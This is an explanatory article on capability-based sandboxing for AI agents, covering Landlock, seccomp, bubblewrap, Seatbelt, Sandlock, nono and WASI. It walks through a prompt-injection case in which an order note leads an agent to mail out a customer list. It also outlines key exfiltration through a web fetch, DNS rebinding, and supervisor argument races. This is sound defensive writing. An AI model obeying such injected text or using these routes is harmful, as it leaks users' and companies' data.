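# Lightweight capability-based security layers for AI agents as an alternative to full virtual machines

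## What a capability is, and what a virtual machine leaves open

An AI agent is a language model that acts by calling tools in a loop. The model itself produces only text. A second program, the host, sends it a task along with descriptions of some tools: one that queries a database, perhaps, and one that sends mail. When the model's output names a tool and supplies arguments for it, the host carries out the call and appends the result to the text the model reads next. This goes on until the model produces an answer instead of a call. (If one of the tools runs shell commands or program code, that code acts on the computer directly, and the host sees only what went in and what came out.)

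By default, an agent's calls can usually reach everything the user can reach. Capability-based security layers instead give the agent access to particular things, such as one folder, one database table, or mail to one address. They are lightweight because they don't need a separate operating system for each agent. A virtual machine, the heavier and more familiar option, is a simulated computer with its own operating system, which keeps whatever runs inside it away from the real machine. The two protections overlap, but a virtual machine doesn't prevent a kind of failure to which agents are especially prone, so it isn't simply a stronger version of the same protection.

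### Ambient authority

To open a file or a network connection, a process (a running program) makes a request, known as a system call, to the kernel, the core of the operating system, which controls the hardware. Mainstream kernels allow or deny most such requests based on the user account the process belongs to. If a sales clerk starts a host, the host can therefore open anything the clerk can, and so can the agent acting through it.

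The problem is much older than language models. *Robust Composition* (Miller, 2006) illustrates it with Solitaire. The game needs to save a score in one file, but it runs with all of its user's authority. It could delete any of the user's files, search their email for something to sell, or install a back door. The game probably does none of this, but an attacker who exploits the right bug in it could.

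In *Capability Myths Demolished*, Miller, Yee and Shapiro (2003) define ambient authority as authority that a program exercises without selecting it. They compare it to a door that has no key and opens for the right people. On Unix, for example, a program opens a file by passing its name, without presenting a credential, and succeeds or fails depending on whose account it runs under.

Agents tend to gather ambient authority from several places at once. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting agents to outside tools, lets one agent use many tool servers together. As Semgrep's *Security Like It's 1977* (2026) points out, the agent's authority is then the union of what they all offer:

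authority = filesystem ∪ database ∪ email ∪ shell

Text that arrives through any one of the four can trigger a call to any other. Semgrep, a software-security company, makes this point to support its own proposed protocol change, but the point doesn't depend on that proposal. Better logins don't help much either, because MCP relies on OAuth for authorization. OAuth can determine whether a user may use a server, but not whether a particular operation, prompted by a particular piece of text, should touch a particular record.

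### The orders example

Suppose a sales clerk asks an agent to total the pending orders and email the sum to a manager. The host offers the agent two tools that both use the clerk's accounts. One runs any query on the company database, which holds an orders table and a customers table. The other sends mail to any address. Three orders are pending, for $1,200, $450 and $2,350, so the correct total is $4,000.

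Each order has a notes field, which the customer fills in. Where the second order should have delivery instructions, the customer has written that whoever is processing the order should send the full customer list to an outside address.

The agent queries the pending orders, and the database returns the rows with their notes. The model's input now contains both the note and the clerk's request, and nothing in it reliably separates instructions from data. If the model follows the note, it queries the customers table and calls the mail tool with the outside address. The database accepts the query because the clerk may read that table, and the mail server accepts the message because the clerk may email anyone. The agent then adds up the orders and emails the total, $4,000, to the manager, so the clerk sees a finished task.

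This is prompt injection, in which text in material the agent reads steers it toward an attacker's goal. Whether the note works depends on the model and the wording. The access rules don't affect the outcome, because the clerk had permission to take every step.

### The confused deputy

In *The Confused Deputy* (1988), Hardy tells a "nearly true story" from about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that rented out time on shared computers. The staff wanted statistics on which language features people used, so they gave the compiler a licence to write files in its own directory, SYSX, where it kept the statistics in a file named STAT. The compiler would also write debugging output to any file the user named. The billing records were in the same directory, in a file named BILL. A user learned that name and gave it as the file for the debugging output. Because the compiler had a licence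 to write in that directory, the operating system allowed it to overwrite the billing records.

Hardy considers the obvious fixes. The compiler could refuse any name in SYSX, but some users might have legitimate reasons to use files there. It could refuse the name BILL, but other files were sensitive too, and someone would have to change the compiler whenever a new one appeared. Tymshare added a system call that let the compiler choose between its own authority and its user's. Soon some programs needed to choose among more than two authorities, and for operations on things other than files. When Hardy last wrote down the conditions under which a program could open a file, they contained fourteen ANDs and ORs.

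On this account, the underlying problem arose because the compiler held authority from two sources and could not specify which one to use for each purpose. That made it a confused deputy, a program tricked into using its own authority for someone who lacks it.

The order note does to the agent what the name BILL did to the compiler. The customer who wrote the note cannot read the customers table, but the agent can, and reads it for the customer. The agent is, if anything, in a worse position than the compiler. The compiler followed a fixed path, so a programmer could at least find each place where it opened a file. An agent works out its next step from a single text that contains both the clerk's request and the customer's note. Instructing it beforehand never to mail out the customer list is much like teaching the compiler to recognize the name BILL, because it covers only one sensitive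 thing that somebody thought of.

### Capabilities and access-control lists

Hardy's solution was to replace file names with capabilities. A capability is an unforgeable reference that both names a resource and permits its use. The compiler would hold one for the statistics file, and the user would give it another for the debugging output. A user with no right to write to BILL would have no capability for that file to give the compiler, and so could not make the request that destroyed the billing records.

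Two ordinary Unix commands show the difference. Both of these copy one file into another:

`cp foo.txt bar.txt`

`cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`

In the first, as Miller explains, the shell passes `cp` two pieces of text. To turn them into files, `cp` needs the right to open anything its user might name, which is to say the user's whole file system. In the second the shell opens the two files itself and passes `cat` two open file descriptors, which are close relatives of capabilities. To do its job `cat` needs those two and nothing else. (In practice Unix gives it the user's full authority anyway.)

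Most operating systems are built around access-control lists instead. Such a list belongs to a resource and records who may use it. A table of subjects and objects makes the two arrangements look like the same thing:

| | Orders table | Customers table | Mail to the manager |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sales clerk | read, write | read | send |
| Billing program | read | read | none |
| Agent totalling orders | read | none | send |

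Each column of the table is an access-control list, and each row is a list of capabilities. Miller and colleagues wrote their paper partly to dispute the common view that the choice between the two is a matter of bookkeeping. They argue that the table is a snapshot, while security depends on how its cells change. The table also doesn't show which way the references point. An access-control list points from the resource to the subject, so the subject needs a separate way to name the resource. When names and permissions are passed separately, a program like Tymshare's compiler can use a name with the wrong permission.

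Their other objection, which applies even more directly to agents, is that someone has to update an access-control list whenever its subjects change. This is manageable for employees but impractical for processes that start and stop every second. Systems with such lists therefore group processes under user accounts. In 2003 the three knew of no implementation that treated individual processes as separate subjects. In such a system, the table above would have no bottom row, and the agent would run as the sales clerk with all the clerk's permissions.

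### How a program comes to hold a capability

Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn, at MIT, set out the idea in 1966 in a design for computers that run many people's programs at once. Each computation had a list of capabilities, called the C-list, which the supervisor (roughly, the kernel) maintained. The program could refer to a capability only by its position in the list. Unix file descriptors work similarly. The kernel keeps a table for each program that maps numbers to open files, so sending the number 3 to another program doesn't give that program access to the file.

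In some systems a capability is just a long secret string of bits, which, as Miller and colleagues note, can go wherever data can go. If an agent's host puts such a string in the model's input, the model can copy it into an email. If the host keeps the real references to itself and lets the model write only "resource 3", the model's text contains no capability that someone could steal.

The strict modern version is the object-capability model, in which everything is an object and objects can affect one another only by sending messages along references they hold. Miller describes his rules for this model as essentially a restatement of earlier ones by Carl Hewitt and Henry Baker. Under these rules, an object can get a reference in four ways.

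- Initial conditions. The object already held the reference when the period under study began, as a host might already have a connection to the database.
- Parenthood. An object that creates another holds, at that moment, the only reference to it. An agent that creates a scratch file can use that file.
- Endowment. A creator can equip the new object with references that the creator itself holds. The host can start the agent with a reference to the pending orders.
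- Introduction. An object that holds references to two others can send one of them a reference to the other. Halfway through the task, the host can pass the agent a reference to a mail sender.

Those four ways are the only ones, so two groups of objects with no path between them can never acquire one. This also answers the old complaint that anyone with a capability can pass it to anyone else, because a holder can pass it only to an object it can already reach. All of this depends on programs having no way around the rules. A language that lets programs turn integers into pointers breaks the rules, and so does one with global variables through which any two objects can communicate.

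Under these rules the customer's note gives the agent no authority, because the words "customer list" are not a reference to the customers table. But if the agent already holds such a reference, the words are enough, because the agent supplies the authority itself. Miller and colleagues say that removing ambient authority makes it possible to write a deputy that nobody can confuse, provided the deputy keeps track of what each of its capabilities is for. A compiler can do that, but nobody should rely on a language model to do it while reading text from strangers, so security depends more on which capabilities the host grants in the first place.

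### Least privilege, attenuation and revocation

Under the principle of least privilege, every program and every user should work with the smallest set of privileges the job requires. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) presents this as one of eight design principles, and two of the others are also relevant here. The default should be no access, so that a mistake shows up as a refusal, which people notice. The system should also check every access to every object.

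Miller prefers the term "least authority" and emphasizes when authority is granted. A policy file that fixes a program's access at launch has to allow everything the program might need, and those needs change as it runs. Miller would grant authority with each request, when the need arises. Predicting these needs is even harder for an agent, because its next step depends on what it has just read.

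Capabilities rarely match a task exactly, so programs derive narrower ones from broader ones, which is called attenuation. In the orders example, the host could keep the full database connection and wrap it in an object whose only operation returns the numbers and amounts of pending orders. A second wrapper, around the mail account, could send messages only to the manager. The agent gets only these two wrappers. Because the first wrapper leaves notes out, the note never reaches the model. If the task required the notes, the model might still follow the instruction, but it would have no call that reads customer data or emails a stranger. The instruction could still lead it to send the manager a wrong total, which capabilities can't prevent because the task allows the agent to send the manager a total.

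Revocation, the withdrawal of a capability after someone has granted it, uses the same technique. David Redell described how to do it in 1974, although critics long held that it was impossible in capability systems because nobody can reach into a program and remove a reference it holds. The grantor hands over a forwarder instead of a direct reference to the resource, and keeps a switch that turns the forwarder off. The forwarder passes messages on to the resource until it is switched off, after which it stops working for the recipient and for anyone the recipient passed it to. Miller describes the method's limits. If the resource ever gives out a direct reference to itself, the recipient can bypass the forwarder, and the grantor needs a more elaborate wrapper (a "membrane") that also wraps every reference passing through. Revocation also can't take back data the agent has already read, such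 as a customer list.

Wrappers make it harder to see what an agent can do. Miller distinguishes permission, meaning the references an object holds directly, from authority, meaning the effects it can bring about, including through others. Suppose the agent has no tool for outside mail but can post comments on an order, and the order system emails every comment to the customer. The agent has no permission to send mail outside the company, and it has the authority to do so. Working out a program's eventual authority exactly (EA, in Miller's notation) is intractable, because it depends on how every program involved behaves. One can work out a larger set, TA, by looking only at who holds references to what and assuming that every object might do anything its references allow. Taking account of the known behaviour of some objects gives a tighter set, BA:

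EA ⊆ BA ⊆ TA

If outside mail is not in BA, it is not in EA either, and the design is safe in that respect. For an agent, it is sensible to assume the worst about the model's behaviour and to rely on known behaviour only for the wrappers, which are short enough for a person to read.

### What a virtual machine separates

Virtual machines began as a way to share one large computer among many users. People now also use them to contain untrusted code that might break through the operating system and take over the computer, which is a different worry from Hardy's. *Let's discuss sandbox isolation* (2026), a survey of the options for running untrusted code, reports that the Linux kernel has roughly 340 system calls, with tens of millions of lines of code behind them. A flaw in any call that a process can make is a possible way into the kernel, and from there into everything else on the machine.

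A container is one or more processes that the kernel gives a restricted view of the computer, with their own file tree, network interfaces and process list. They still make system calls to the same kernel as everything else on the machine. A virtual machine has its own kernel, and a hypervisor uses processor features to isolate its memory from the rest of the machine. A microVM is a virtual machine without a full one's emulation of old hardware, so it starts in milliseconds. Code that takes over the kernel inside either kind of virtual machine still has to get through the hypervisor or the simulated devices, which is much harder.

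In 1975, Saltzer and Schroeder classed VM/370, IBM's virtual machine system, among the "all-or-nothing systems", which isolate users from one another and, where they allow sharing, share with everyone alike. As far as protection goes, a user on a purely isolated system is in the same position as someone with a private computer. So is an agent in a virtual machine, but this leaves open what else is on that computer.

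If the orders agent runs in a microVM, it can't reach other people's workloads on the same server, or files on the clerk's laptop unless someone copies or mounts them inside. That isolation is useful, but the agent has to read orders and send mail, so someone puts the database password and mail credentials in the microVM too. When the agent reads the note, it still queries the customers table and mails the list to the outside address. This requires no kernel exploit or hypervisor failure. In another common layout, only the code that the model writes runs in the virtual machine, and the host makes the database and mail calls from outside, so the theft doesn't pass through the virtual machine at all.

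Replacing the password inside the virtual machine with one for a database account that can read only pending orders would keep the customer list safe. This is attenuation. The protection comes from the narrower account and would be the same without the virtual machine.

The other natural reply is to restrict the network. *Let's discuss sandbox isolation* argues for this because an attacker who can't escape a microVM can still send out every secret the code inside can read if the network is open. A list of approved destinations would stop the agent from posting the customer list to a strange website, but it would not stop the email. The company's mail server has to be approved because the manager's $4,000 goes out through it, and a message to the outside address uses the same connection to the same server. Telling the two messages apart requires checking the recipient, which only the mail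 tool, the mail server, or the host that makes the call can do.

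## Restricting an ordinary process with the operating system

A mail tool can check a recipient because the host sends the message itself. But a shell command can start a compiler, a package installer or a script that nobody has read, and these programs then make their own system calls. The host can inspect the command beforehand, but often can't tell from it what the programs will do. The kernel can check what they access, because every attempt to open a file or a connection passes through it. Linux, macOS and Windows can all give a process less access than its user has, and coding agents, which do much of their work in a shell, depend on this.

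### One command, from request to exit

Suppose the sales clerk has exported the pending orders to a folder, and the agent has a tool that runs shell commands. Each line of `orders.csv` holds an order number, an amount and a note. The agent asks the host to run this:

`awk -F, '{s += $2} END {print s}' orders.csv > total.txt`

The command adds up the second column and saves the result. On Linux, a host with a sandbox first creates a child process, which starts with all the clerk's authority. The child gives up most of that authority before it loads any of the command's code. From then on, it can read the system's program folders and the orders folder, but it can write only in the orders folder and cannot open network connections. *Sandlock* (Wang and Zheng, 2026), a design for an open-source sandbox, makes the child wait at this point until the host confirms that its monitoring is in place.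 Then the child replaces itself with the shell.

The child process can tighten these restrictions later but can't loosen them, and every program it starts inherits them. The same restrictions therefore apply to `awk` whether the shell runs it directly or through three layers of scripts.

The shell makes a system call to open `total.txt` for writing. The kernel checks the clerk's own permissions and then the sandbox's rules, and both allow it. `awk` opens `orders.csv`, writes 4000 and exits. The host collects the exit code and any printed output, and appends them to the model's next input.

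If the customer's note leads the model to try uploading the customer list with `curl`, the host launches that command in the same way. `curl` starts normally, but the kernel blocks it from opening the list, which is outside the orders folder, and the model gets an error message. If the clerk had exported the list to the orders folder too, `curl` could read it, and only the network restriction would stop the upload.

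### What each mechanism restricts

Linux has no single sandbox, so hosts assemble one from several parts.

Landlock mainly restricts access to files. A process lists folders and the kinds of access to allow beneath each, then applies these rules to itself, which requires no administrator rights. Later versions can also restrict TCP ports and, from Linux 6.12, signals and some local sockets between processes. Landlock can limit a process to port 443, the usual port for encrypted web traffic, but it can't restrict which hosts the process connects to on that port. Files already open when the rules take effect stay open.

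Seccomp restricts system calls. The host loads a small filter into the kernel, and the filter receives the number of each call and its raw arguments. It can allow the call, block it, or pause it while another process decides. For example, it can stop a program from creating any network sockets. But the filter can't identify which file a program is trying to open, because the argument is only the memory address of the file's name. Sandboxes therefore pair seccomp with another mechanism to restrict file access.

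Bubblewrap limits what a command can see of the system. It uses namespaces, the kernel feature behind containers, to build a private file tree from folders the host picks, each either read-only or writable. The command has no path to files outside the tree. Bubblewrap can also give the command its own process list and a network with nothing connected to it. However, it usually needs permission to create "user namespaces", which some Linux distributions withhold from ordinary users. OpenAI's *Sandbox*, part of the documentation for its coding agent Codex, includes a shell command that lifts this restriction, but it does so for every program on the machine.

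These parts are partly interchangeable. Willison's *OpenAI Codex CLI Sandbox Implementation Analysis* (November 2025) reported that Codex used Landlock to restrict file access and seccomp to block the network. By May 2026, OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* listed bubblewrap and seccomp as the default.

On macOS, Seatbelt restricts files, the network and other operations together. The host writes a profile, a text description of what to allow, and uses `sandbox-exec` to start the command under it. The kernel enforces the profile on the command and its descendants. Because the profile is text, the host can easily generate a different one for each situation.

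Sandboxing Codex took more work on Windows. It had no sandbox there in September 2025, so users either approved nearly every command or gave the agent full access. In *Building a safe, effective sandbox to enable Codex on Windows*, Wiesen explains how OpenAI built one and why it didn't use the features Windows already had. AppContainer, the native sandbox, suits an app whose needs are known in advance, but a coding agent runs Git, Python and whatever else it decides on. Windows Sandbox is a disposable virtual machine, so it would have cut the agent off from the user's files and tools, and home editions of Windows lack it. Integrity labels would have opened the working folder to every low-trust process on the machine.

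OpenAI settled on write-restricted tokens. A token is Windows' record of a process's identity and privileges. With a write-restricted token, a write succeeds only if both the user and at least one identity on a second list attached to the token have permission. Codex creates an identity that belongs to no person, adds it to that list, and gives it write access to the working folder. The list also has to include the built-in identity "Everyone", so a folder that everyone can write to remains writable. The second check doesn't apply to reads.

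The restricted token does not limit network access. OpenAI's first prototype set environment variables that directed web traffic to a dead address, and put fake `ssh` and `scp` programs where the shell would find them first. This stopped ordinary tools, but any program could ignore the variables and open a connection directly, and Wiesen calls the protection "only advisory". Windows Firewall could block traffic properly, but it could not single out processes with a restricted token. The current version therefore creates two extra local users, blocks all outgoing traffic for one of them, and runs commands as one or the other. Setting this up requires administrator rights.

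Windows has since gained MXC, a mechanism that suits agents better. Unsloth, an application for running AI models, introduced operating-system sandboxing in October 2026 and uses MXC for it on Windows. Unsloth describes MXC as an official part of Windows 11 from version 24H2 onward.

### Allowing some hosts and blocking the rest

Agents often need to reach a few sites, such as a package registry or a documentation site. Landlock and seccomp can't filter connections by host name, so a common approach is to block the command's direct network access and run a proxy, a program outside the sandbox that makes connections for the command.

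Suppose the list of allowed domains contains only `pypi.org`, where Python packages come from. The sandbox lets the command connect only to the local proxy, and the host sets environment variables that direct tools there. When a package installer requests a connection to `pypi.org` on port 443, the proxy checks the name against the list, opens the connection, and relays data in both directions. It refuses requests for any other name. Because the installer encrypts its traffic, the proxy can identify the destination but can't read the data.

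The environment variables only help tools find the proxy. The closed network enforces the list, as OpenAI's Windows prototype showed. In Codex, network access and the proxy are separate settings, both off by default. According to OpenAI, turning on only network access gives commands unrestricted outbound connections.

Filtering by name is also imperfect, because whoever controls an allowed name can change the address it resolves to. In this attack, called DNS rebinding, a request for a harmless-looking site can end up at a database inside the company. Codex looks up each name and blocks those that resolve to private addresses, but OpenAI describes the check as best-effort, because ruling out the attack would require keeping the address fixed for the whole connection. Sandlock looks up every allowed name once, when the sandbox starts, and permits only the addresses it finds, so users can't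 allow a whole family of names with a wildcard.

Permission to contact a host may be too broad even when the host is correctly identified. A command that may contact a code-hosting site to download a library can usually upload data to an attacker's account there. The company's mail server posed the same problem in the orders example. Sandlock can restrict individual web addresses and distinguish reading from writing, but for encrypted traffic its proxy must decrypt each request first. The command then has to trust a certificate authority that belongs to the sandbox, so Wang and Zheng made decryption optional.

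### Access rules that imitate capabilities

None of the mechanisms described so far uses capabilities in the strict sense. The process supplies a file name, as `cp` does, and the kernel checks its rules to decide whether the process may open that file. The name is still separate from the permission, as it was for Hardy's compiler.

The improvement is that Landlock and Seatbelt rules can apply to a single command, even one that runs for a tenth of a second. The agent's commands can therefore have their own row in the table of subjects and objects, instead of sharing the clerk's.

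A sandboxed program still has ambient authority within its limits, meaning it can open anything the rules allow without anyone handing it over. Codex makes the working folder writable, so it has to exclude the `.git`, `.codex` and `.agents` folders inside it. A command that could write to `.git` might leave a script there for Git to run later, perhaps outside the sandbox and with all the user's access. The exclusions help, but like a compiler's refusal to write to BILL, they cover only the names that somebody recognized as dangerous.

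Bubblewrap comes closer to capabilities because a command cannot name anything outside the directory tree it receives, though it can still open everything inside that tree by name.

Robert Watson, Jonathan Anderson, Ben Laurie and Kris Kennaway introduced Capsicum, a strict version of this approach, in 2010 for FreeBSD, an operating system similar to Linux. A process makes one call to enter "capability mode" and can never leave. The kernel then refuses system calls that refer to things by global names, such as a path from the top of the file system or the address of another computer. The process can still use file descriptors that it already holds or that another process passes to it. A descriptor for a folder lets it open files beneath that folder but not outside it. Each descriptor also carries a list of rights, such as reading, writing or changing position in the file. Capsicum builds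 in attenuation by letting the process remove rights from this list but not add them.

With Capsicum, the host could open `orders.csv` for reading and `total.txt` for writing, then start a suitably adapted `awk` with only those two descriptors. A customer file in the same folder would be inaccessible because `awk` would have no way to open it.

Adapting programs to capability mode is difficult because most of them find things by name. Python opens its libraries by path, and Git looks for settings in the user's home folder, so both fail in capability mode unless someone changes them or a helper opens the files for them. Access rules don't require changes to programs. Wang and Zheng ran Python, Node, `make` and `pytest` unmodified under Sandlock after allowing each its temporary folders. Because an agent chooses its programs as it runs, agent designers have valued compatibility over strictness.

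### Codex and Claude Code

In practice, the protection these mechanisms provide depends a good deal on the default settings, as two widely used coding agents show. *Inside the Codex sandbox* (Bolin, 2026) describes how Codex runs commands on the user's own machine within file and network limits that the user controls. Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool* documents a sandbox with the same general aim in Claude Code, the company's coding agent. Except for Codex's environment variables, the defaults below come from OpenAI's accounts of May and June 2026 and Anthropic's documentation as of early December 2026.

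| | Codex on the user's machine | Claude Code |
|---|---|---|
| Sandbox | On | Off until the user enables it |
| Writes, when on | Working folder and temporary folders, minus protected paths | Working folder, a temporary folder and any folders the user has added, minus protected paths |
| Reads, when on | Almost anywhere | Most of the machine, including `~/.ssh` and `~/.aws/credentials` |
| Network, when on | None | Only through a proxy, whose list of allowed hosts starts empty |
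| Environment variables | Inherited from the user's shell, by one developer's account | Inherited from Claude Code, including any secrets |
| Windows without a Linux layer | Separate Windows sandbox | No sandbox |

The entry on Codex's environment variables is based on *custom coding agent sandboxing with nono*, published on fingon.iki.fi by a developer who had used both products. The developer reports that all coding agents launch their tools with the current shell environment. In the cloud version of Codex, OpenAI removes configured secrets before the agent starts work.

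Both products restrict writing much more than reading. Development tools keep libraries and settings all over a machine, so a narrow list of readable folders would break many of them. Users can block particular files in either product, but they have to know which ones to block.

Letting sandboxed commands read most files can expose secrets even if those commands have no network access, because their output goes back to the model and the agent may have other tools. Claude Code's sandbox covers only shell commands. According to Anthropic, the built-in tools for reading files and fetching web pages follow separate permission rules, so the list of allowed hosts doesn't apply to web fetches, and the Read tool may still be able to open a file that the sandbox hides from commands. Local MCP servers run with the user's full access. An injected instruction could therefore get the agent to print a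 cloud key with a sandboxed command, then fetch a page from the attacker's site with the key in its address. The sandbox wouldn't stop that fetch, though the permission rules might block it or require the user's approval.

Codex leaves less outside the sandbox, because OpenAI applies it to the agent's built-in file operations as well as to the commands the agent starts. Outside tools are again handled separately, though Bolin gives an MCP server as an example of something a user can run under the `codex sandbox` command. Codex also always asks for approval before calling an outside tool that its author has labeled destructive, so this safeguard depends on the author's labeling.

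In both products, a command that the sandbox blocks can run outside it if the user agrees. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) gives an illustrative snapshot of 10,000 actions inside OpenAI, of which 9,280 stayed in the sandbox and 720 would have interrupted someone to ask for approval. Interruptions on that scale lead some users to switch the sandbox off.

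Neither sandbox would have prevented the theft in the original orders example, which involved no shell command.

### Sandlock

Wang and Zheng designed Sandlock for commands that an agent runs without administrator rights, many times a minute, on a developer's machine. They first separated the rules that the kernel can enforce alone from those that depend on a running program's requests.

Static rules don't depend on the program's input. For example, a rule may let a command read `/usr`, write in one folder, or connect only on port 443, or it may block certain system calls. Sandlock translates these rules into Landlock rules and a seccomp filter before the command starts, and the kernel then enforces them on its own.

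Other decisions depend on information that exists only while the command runs, such as the address it tries to contact, the arguments it passes to a new program, or the web page it requests. For these, seccomp pauses the system call and notifies a supervisor, which runs outside the sandbox as part of the host. If neither the kernel nor the supervisor can decide reliably, Sandlock refuses the operation.

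Supervisors of this kind have a well-known weakness, which is that a program can change a call's arguments after the supervisor has approved them. Suppose a program stores an allowed address in memory and asks to connect to it. The supervisor reads the address and approves the call. Before the kernel acts, another thread in the program replaces the address with a forbidden one, which the kernel then reads and connects to.

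Sandlock's supervisor avoids this by copying the address once, checking the copy, and using it to make the connection itself on a duplicate of the program's socket. Before checking the arguments of a new program, it freezes every thread and process that could change the memory holding them, and it blocks the call if it can't freeze them all.

The supervisor also lets the host tighten the rules partway through a command. For instance, installing a project's dependencies requires the network but running its tests may not, so the host can watch for the test program to start and then cut off the network. Wang and Zheng caution against using the same feature to block programs by name, since hostile code can rename `curl` or make the same requests without it.

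Sandlock can also hold back a command's file changes so that the host can review them and then keep or discard them. It can't take back anything the command has already sent over the network.

Wang and Zheng measured the cost on a six-core workstation. Sandlock added about 5 milliseconds to the time needed to start a trivial command, for a total of about 6. Docker, the standard container software, took roughly 44 times as long. They then ran Redis, a fast in-memory database, to see whether the sandbox slowed a program that was already running:

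| | No sandbox | Sandlock |
|---|---|---|
| Redis writes per second | 75,500 | 75,200 |
| Redis reads per second | 73,900 | 74,200 |
| Small network message and reply, through the supervisor | 20 microseconds | 55 microseconds |

The Redis differences are within the normal variation between runs, but that test used Sandlock's default static rules. If the user restricts connections to particular hosts, as an agent's user probably would, messages pass through the supervisor, and the last row applies. The extra 35 microseconds are negligible in a call to a language model, which takes at least a tenth of a second. A program that exchanged 10,000 small messages with a database would take about a third of a second longer.

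There is less evidence that Sandlock confines programs. Wang and Zheng ran ten checks, such as reading a file outside the permitted folders, contacting a host that wasn't on the list, and starting too many processes. Sandlock enforced the rules correctly in all ten, but these were straightforward cases in which nobody was trying to break out. Wang and Zheng also say that Sandlock does not defend against flaws in the shared kernel, and they recommend a microVM where users of the same machine may attack each other.

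Published figures for other sandboxes are higher. Wang and Zheng list a startup time of about 30 milliseconds for bubblewrap and similar launchers. Unsloth reports the delay for each tool call in its own application, both with operating-system sandboxing and with a lighter mode that only scans commands and code for forbidden patterns:

| System | Operating-system sandbox | Pattern checks only |
|---|---|---|
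| Linux (bubblewrap) | 50 ms | 3 ms |
| macOS (Seatbelt) | 110 ms | 10 ms |
| Windows (MXC) | 164 ms | 8 ms |

These numbers give a sense of scale but can't be used to rank the mechanisms, because they come from different machines and cover different amounts of work. Over a task with 60 tool calls, Unsloth's sandbox would add 3 seconds on Linux, 6.6 on macOS and almost 10 on Windows, which is little compared with the time the model usually needs. The pattern checks are much faster, but they look for names such as `curl` and `rm`, so they have the weakness Wang and Zheng warn about.

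### A separate sandbox for each tool

Because a process can't loosen its own restrictions, a sandbox that lasts for a whole session has to allow everything that any command in the session will need. If one step installs packages and another reads customer data, every step is allowed to do both. The host can avoid this by starting a new process for each tool call, with rules for that call alone. This is practical because each process takes a few milliseconds to start.

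Sandlock supports it in two ways. A tool server can run each call as a child process with its own policy. Wang and Zheng propose this arrangement but don't test it on a real server. A host can also connect several sandboxed commands in a pipeline. In their example, `cat` is allowed to read a private file and passes its contents to `tr`, which changes them to capital letters. An attacker who took control of `tr` still couldn't open the private folder, and would have only the data that `cat` sent it.

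nono, another open-source sandbox, makes separate authority for each call a main feature. Luke Hinds, who earlier created the software-signing project Sigstore, started it. According to Help Net Security's *Nono* (2026), it uses Landlock on Linux and Seatbelt on macOS, and runs on Windows only through WSL2, which provides a real Linux kernel. Each tool call gets access to the files and network destinations its task requires, along with a stand-in for any password or key, which a proxy outside the sandbox replaces with the real one. This access ends when the call does.

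Part of nono's appeal is that users can set the rules for each tool themselves. The developer behind fingon.iki.fi, who keeps Go build files in unusual folders, switched to nono for all coding agents after having trouble with this setup in their built-in sandboxes. Help Net Security reports that large companies also use nono, and quotes a security engineer at Datadog, a monitoring company, who praises its control over individual commands. In July 2026, however, nono's project page still described it as early alpha software without a security audit.

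With separate sandboxes, the host could let the orders agent's database tool contact only the database server, and its mail tool only the mail server. A malicious library hidden in the mail tool would then have no connection to the customers table. But the customer's note would still work if the tools kept the clerk's accounts, because the model would carry the customer list from one tool to the other. Wang and Zheng acknowledge the same gap in their pipelines, where Sandlock controls what each stage can reach but doesn't examine the data that one stage passes to the next.

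## Runtimes that start with no access

The sandboxes in Codex and Claude Code start with an ordinary process and take away some of its authority. WebAssembly runtimes and some JavaScript runtimes, the programs that load and run code in those languages, instead start code with no access to files or networks. The host program then grants the access the task needs.

### How a WebAssembly module runs

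WebAssembly is an instruction set for a computer that doesn't physically exist. Compilers can turn Rust, C and several other languages into WebAssembly modules, which a runtime then translates into instructions for the real processor. Wasmtime is a runtime that works outside web browsers. The Bytecode Alliance, an industry group, maintains it.

A module has its own memory, a block of bytes. Addresses in its code are positions in that block, and the runtime stops any access past the end, so the module can't compute an address that refers to the host's memory. The instruction set also has no system calls, so a module has to call a host function to affect anything outside its memory. The module file lists the functions it needs as imports, and a module with no imports can do arithmetic but can't open a file.

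Most useful programs need files, so Mozilla's *Standardizing WASI* (2019) announced work on the WebAssembly System Interface (WASI), a standard set of host functions. According to WASI's *Security*, code that uses this interface has no ambient authority.

Suppose the agent has written a program to add up the amounts in `orders.csv`, and the host has compiled it into a module. Before starting the module, the host opens the orders folder and enters it in the module's table of open files as number 3, under the name `/work`. The module calls the "open" function with the number 3 and the name `orders.csv`. The runtime finds the file in that folder and returns the number 4. When the module reads from 4, the runtime copies the file's contents into the module's memory. The module then adds up the amounts and prints the total, 4000.

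If the module tries to open `../customers.csv`, the call fails, because WASI resolves every path inside the folder that the caller supplies. Guessing the number 5 also fails, because the table has no entry there. The table is the same idea as Dennis and Van Horn's C-list, and the system works much like Capsicum. Unlike with Capsicum, a Rust programmer doesn't have to adapt the program by hand, because the standard library turns `/work/orders.csv` into a folder number and a file name.

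WASI has changed how a host grants access. In the first version, a module imports the whole set of functions, and what it can access depends on which open folders the host gives it. The second version introduced components, which have separate imports for resources such as files, networking and clocks. Anyone can check a component's file before running it to see whether it can use the network at all, although the file doesn't show which folders the host will open. The second version also required a program to pass a network handle into each call that opened a connection. The third drops this requirement, so once the host grants a component network access, all the code inside can use it. This is more convenient, but it brings back a little ambient authority within the component.

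### A coding agent without a shell

`wasm_agent.py`, a prototype coding agent from 2026, relies on these restrictions for everything it runs. It has tools for reading, writing and editing files, but no shell, and it can't run Python. It can execute only WebAssembly that it has compiled itself. One tool compiles a Rust file into a module, and another runs the module in Wasmtime, with a `dirs` argument listing the folders to open. Two more tools search Rust's public package index and download packages as source code, without running any of it.

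This is more work than writing a line of `awk`. In one run, the agent wrote a program to print the first ten primes, then changed it to print their sum as well, which took seven tool calls. The module was 1.75 megabytes, mostly because it included Rust's standard library.

Each run has an instruction limit, set in units that Wasmtime calls fuel. Each WebAssembly instruction uses one unit, and the agent's default limit is 20 billion. When the agent's developer ran an infinite loop with a limit of one billion, Wasmtime stopped the program with an error. A time limit would also have stopped the loop, but it can also stop a working program that runs slowly because the machine is busy. With fuel, the same module given the same input stops at the same instruction every time.

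A program that has to update two files can run out of fuel after updating the first, so the developer's claim that running out leaves nothing half done is too strong. Fuel also doesn't limit the time spent in host functions, because it counts only the module's own instructions.

A bigger claim for this design is that anyone can list everything an agent could have changed. The host logs each tool call with its arguments. Each editing call specifies the file it changes, and a module can write only in the folders listed in `dirs`. The log therefore lists every file and folder at risk, which a log entry for a shell command does not do.

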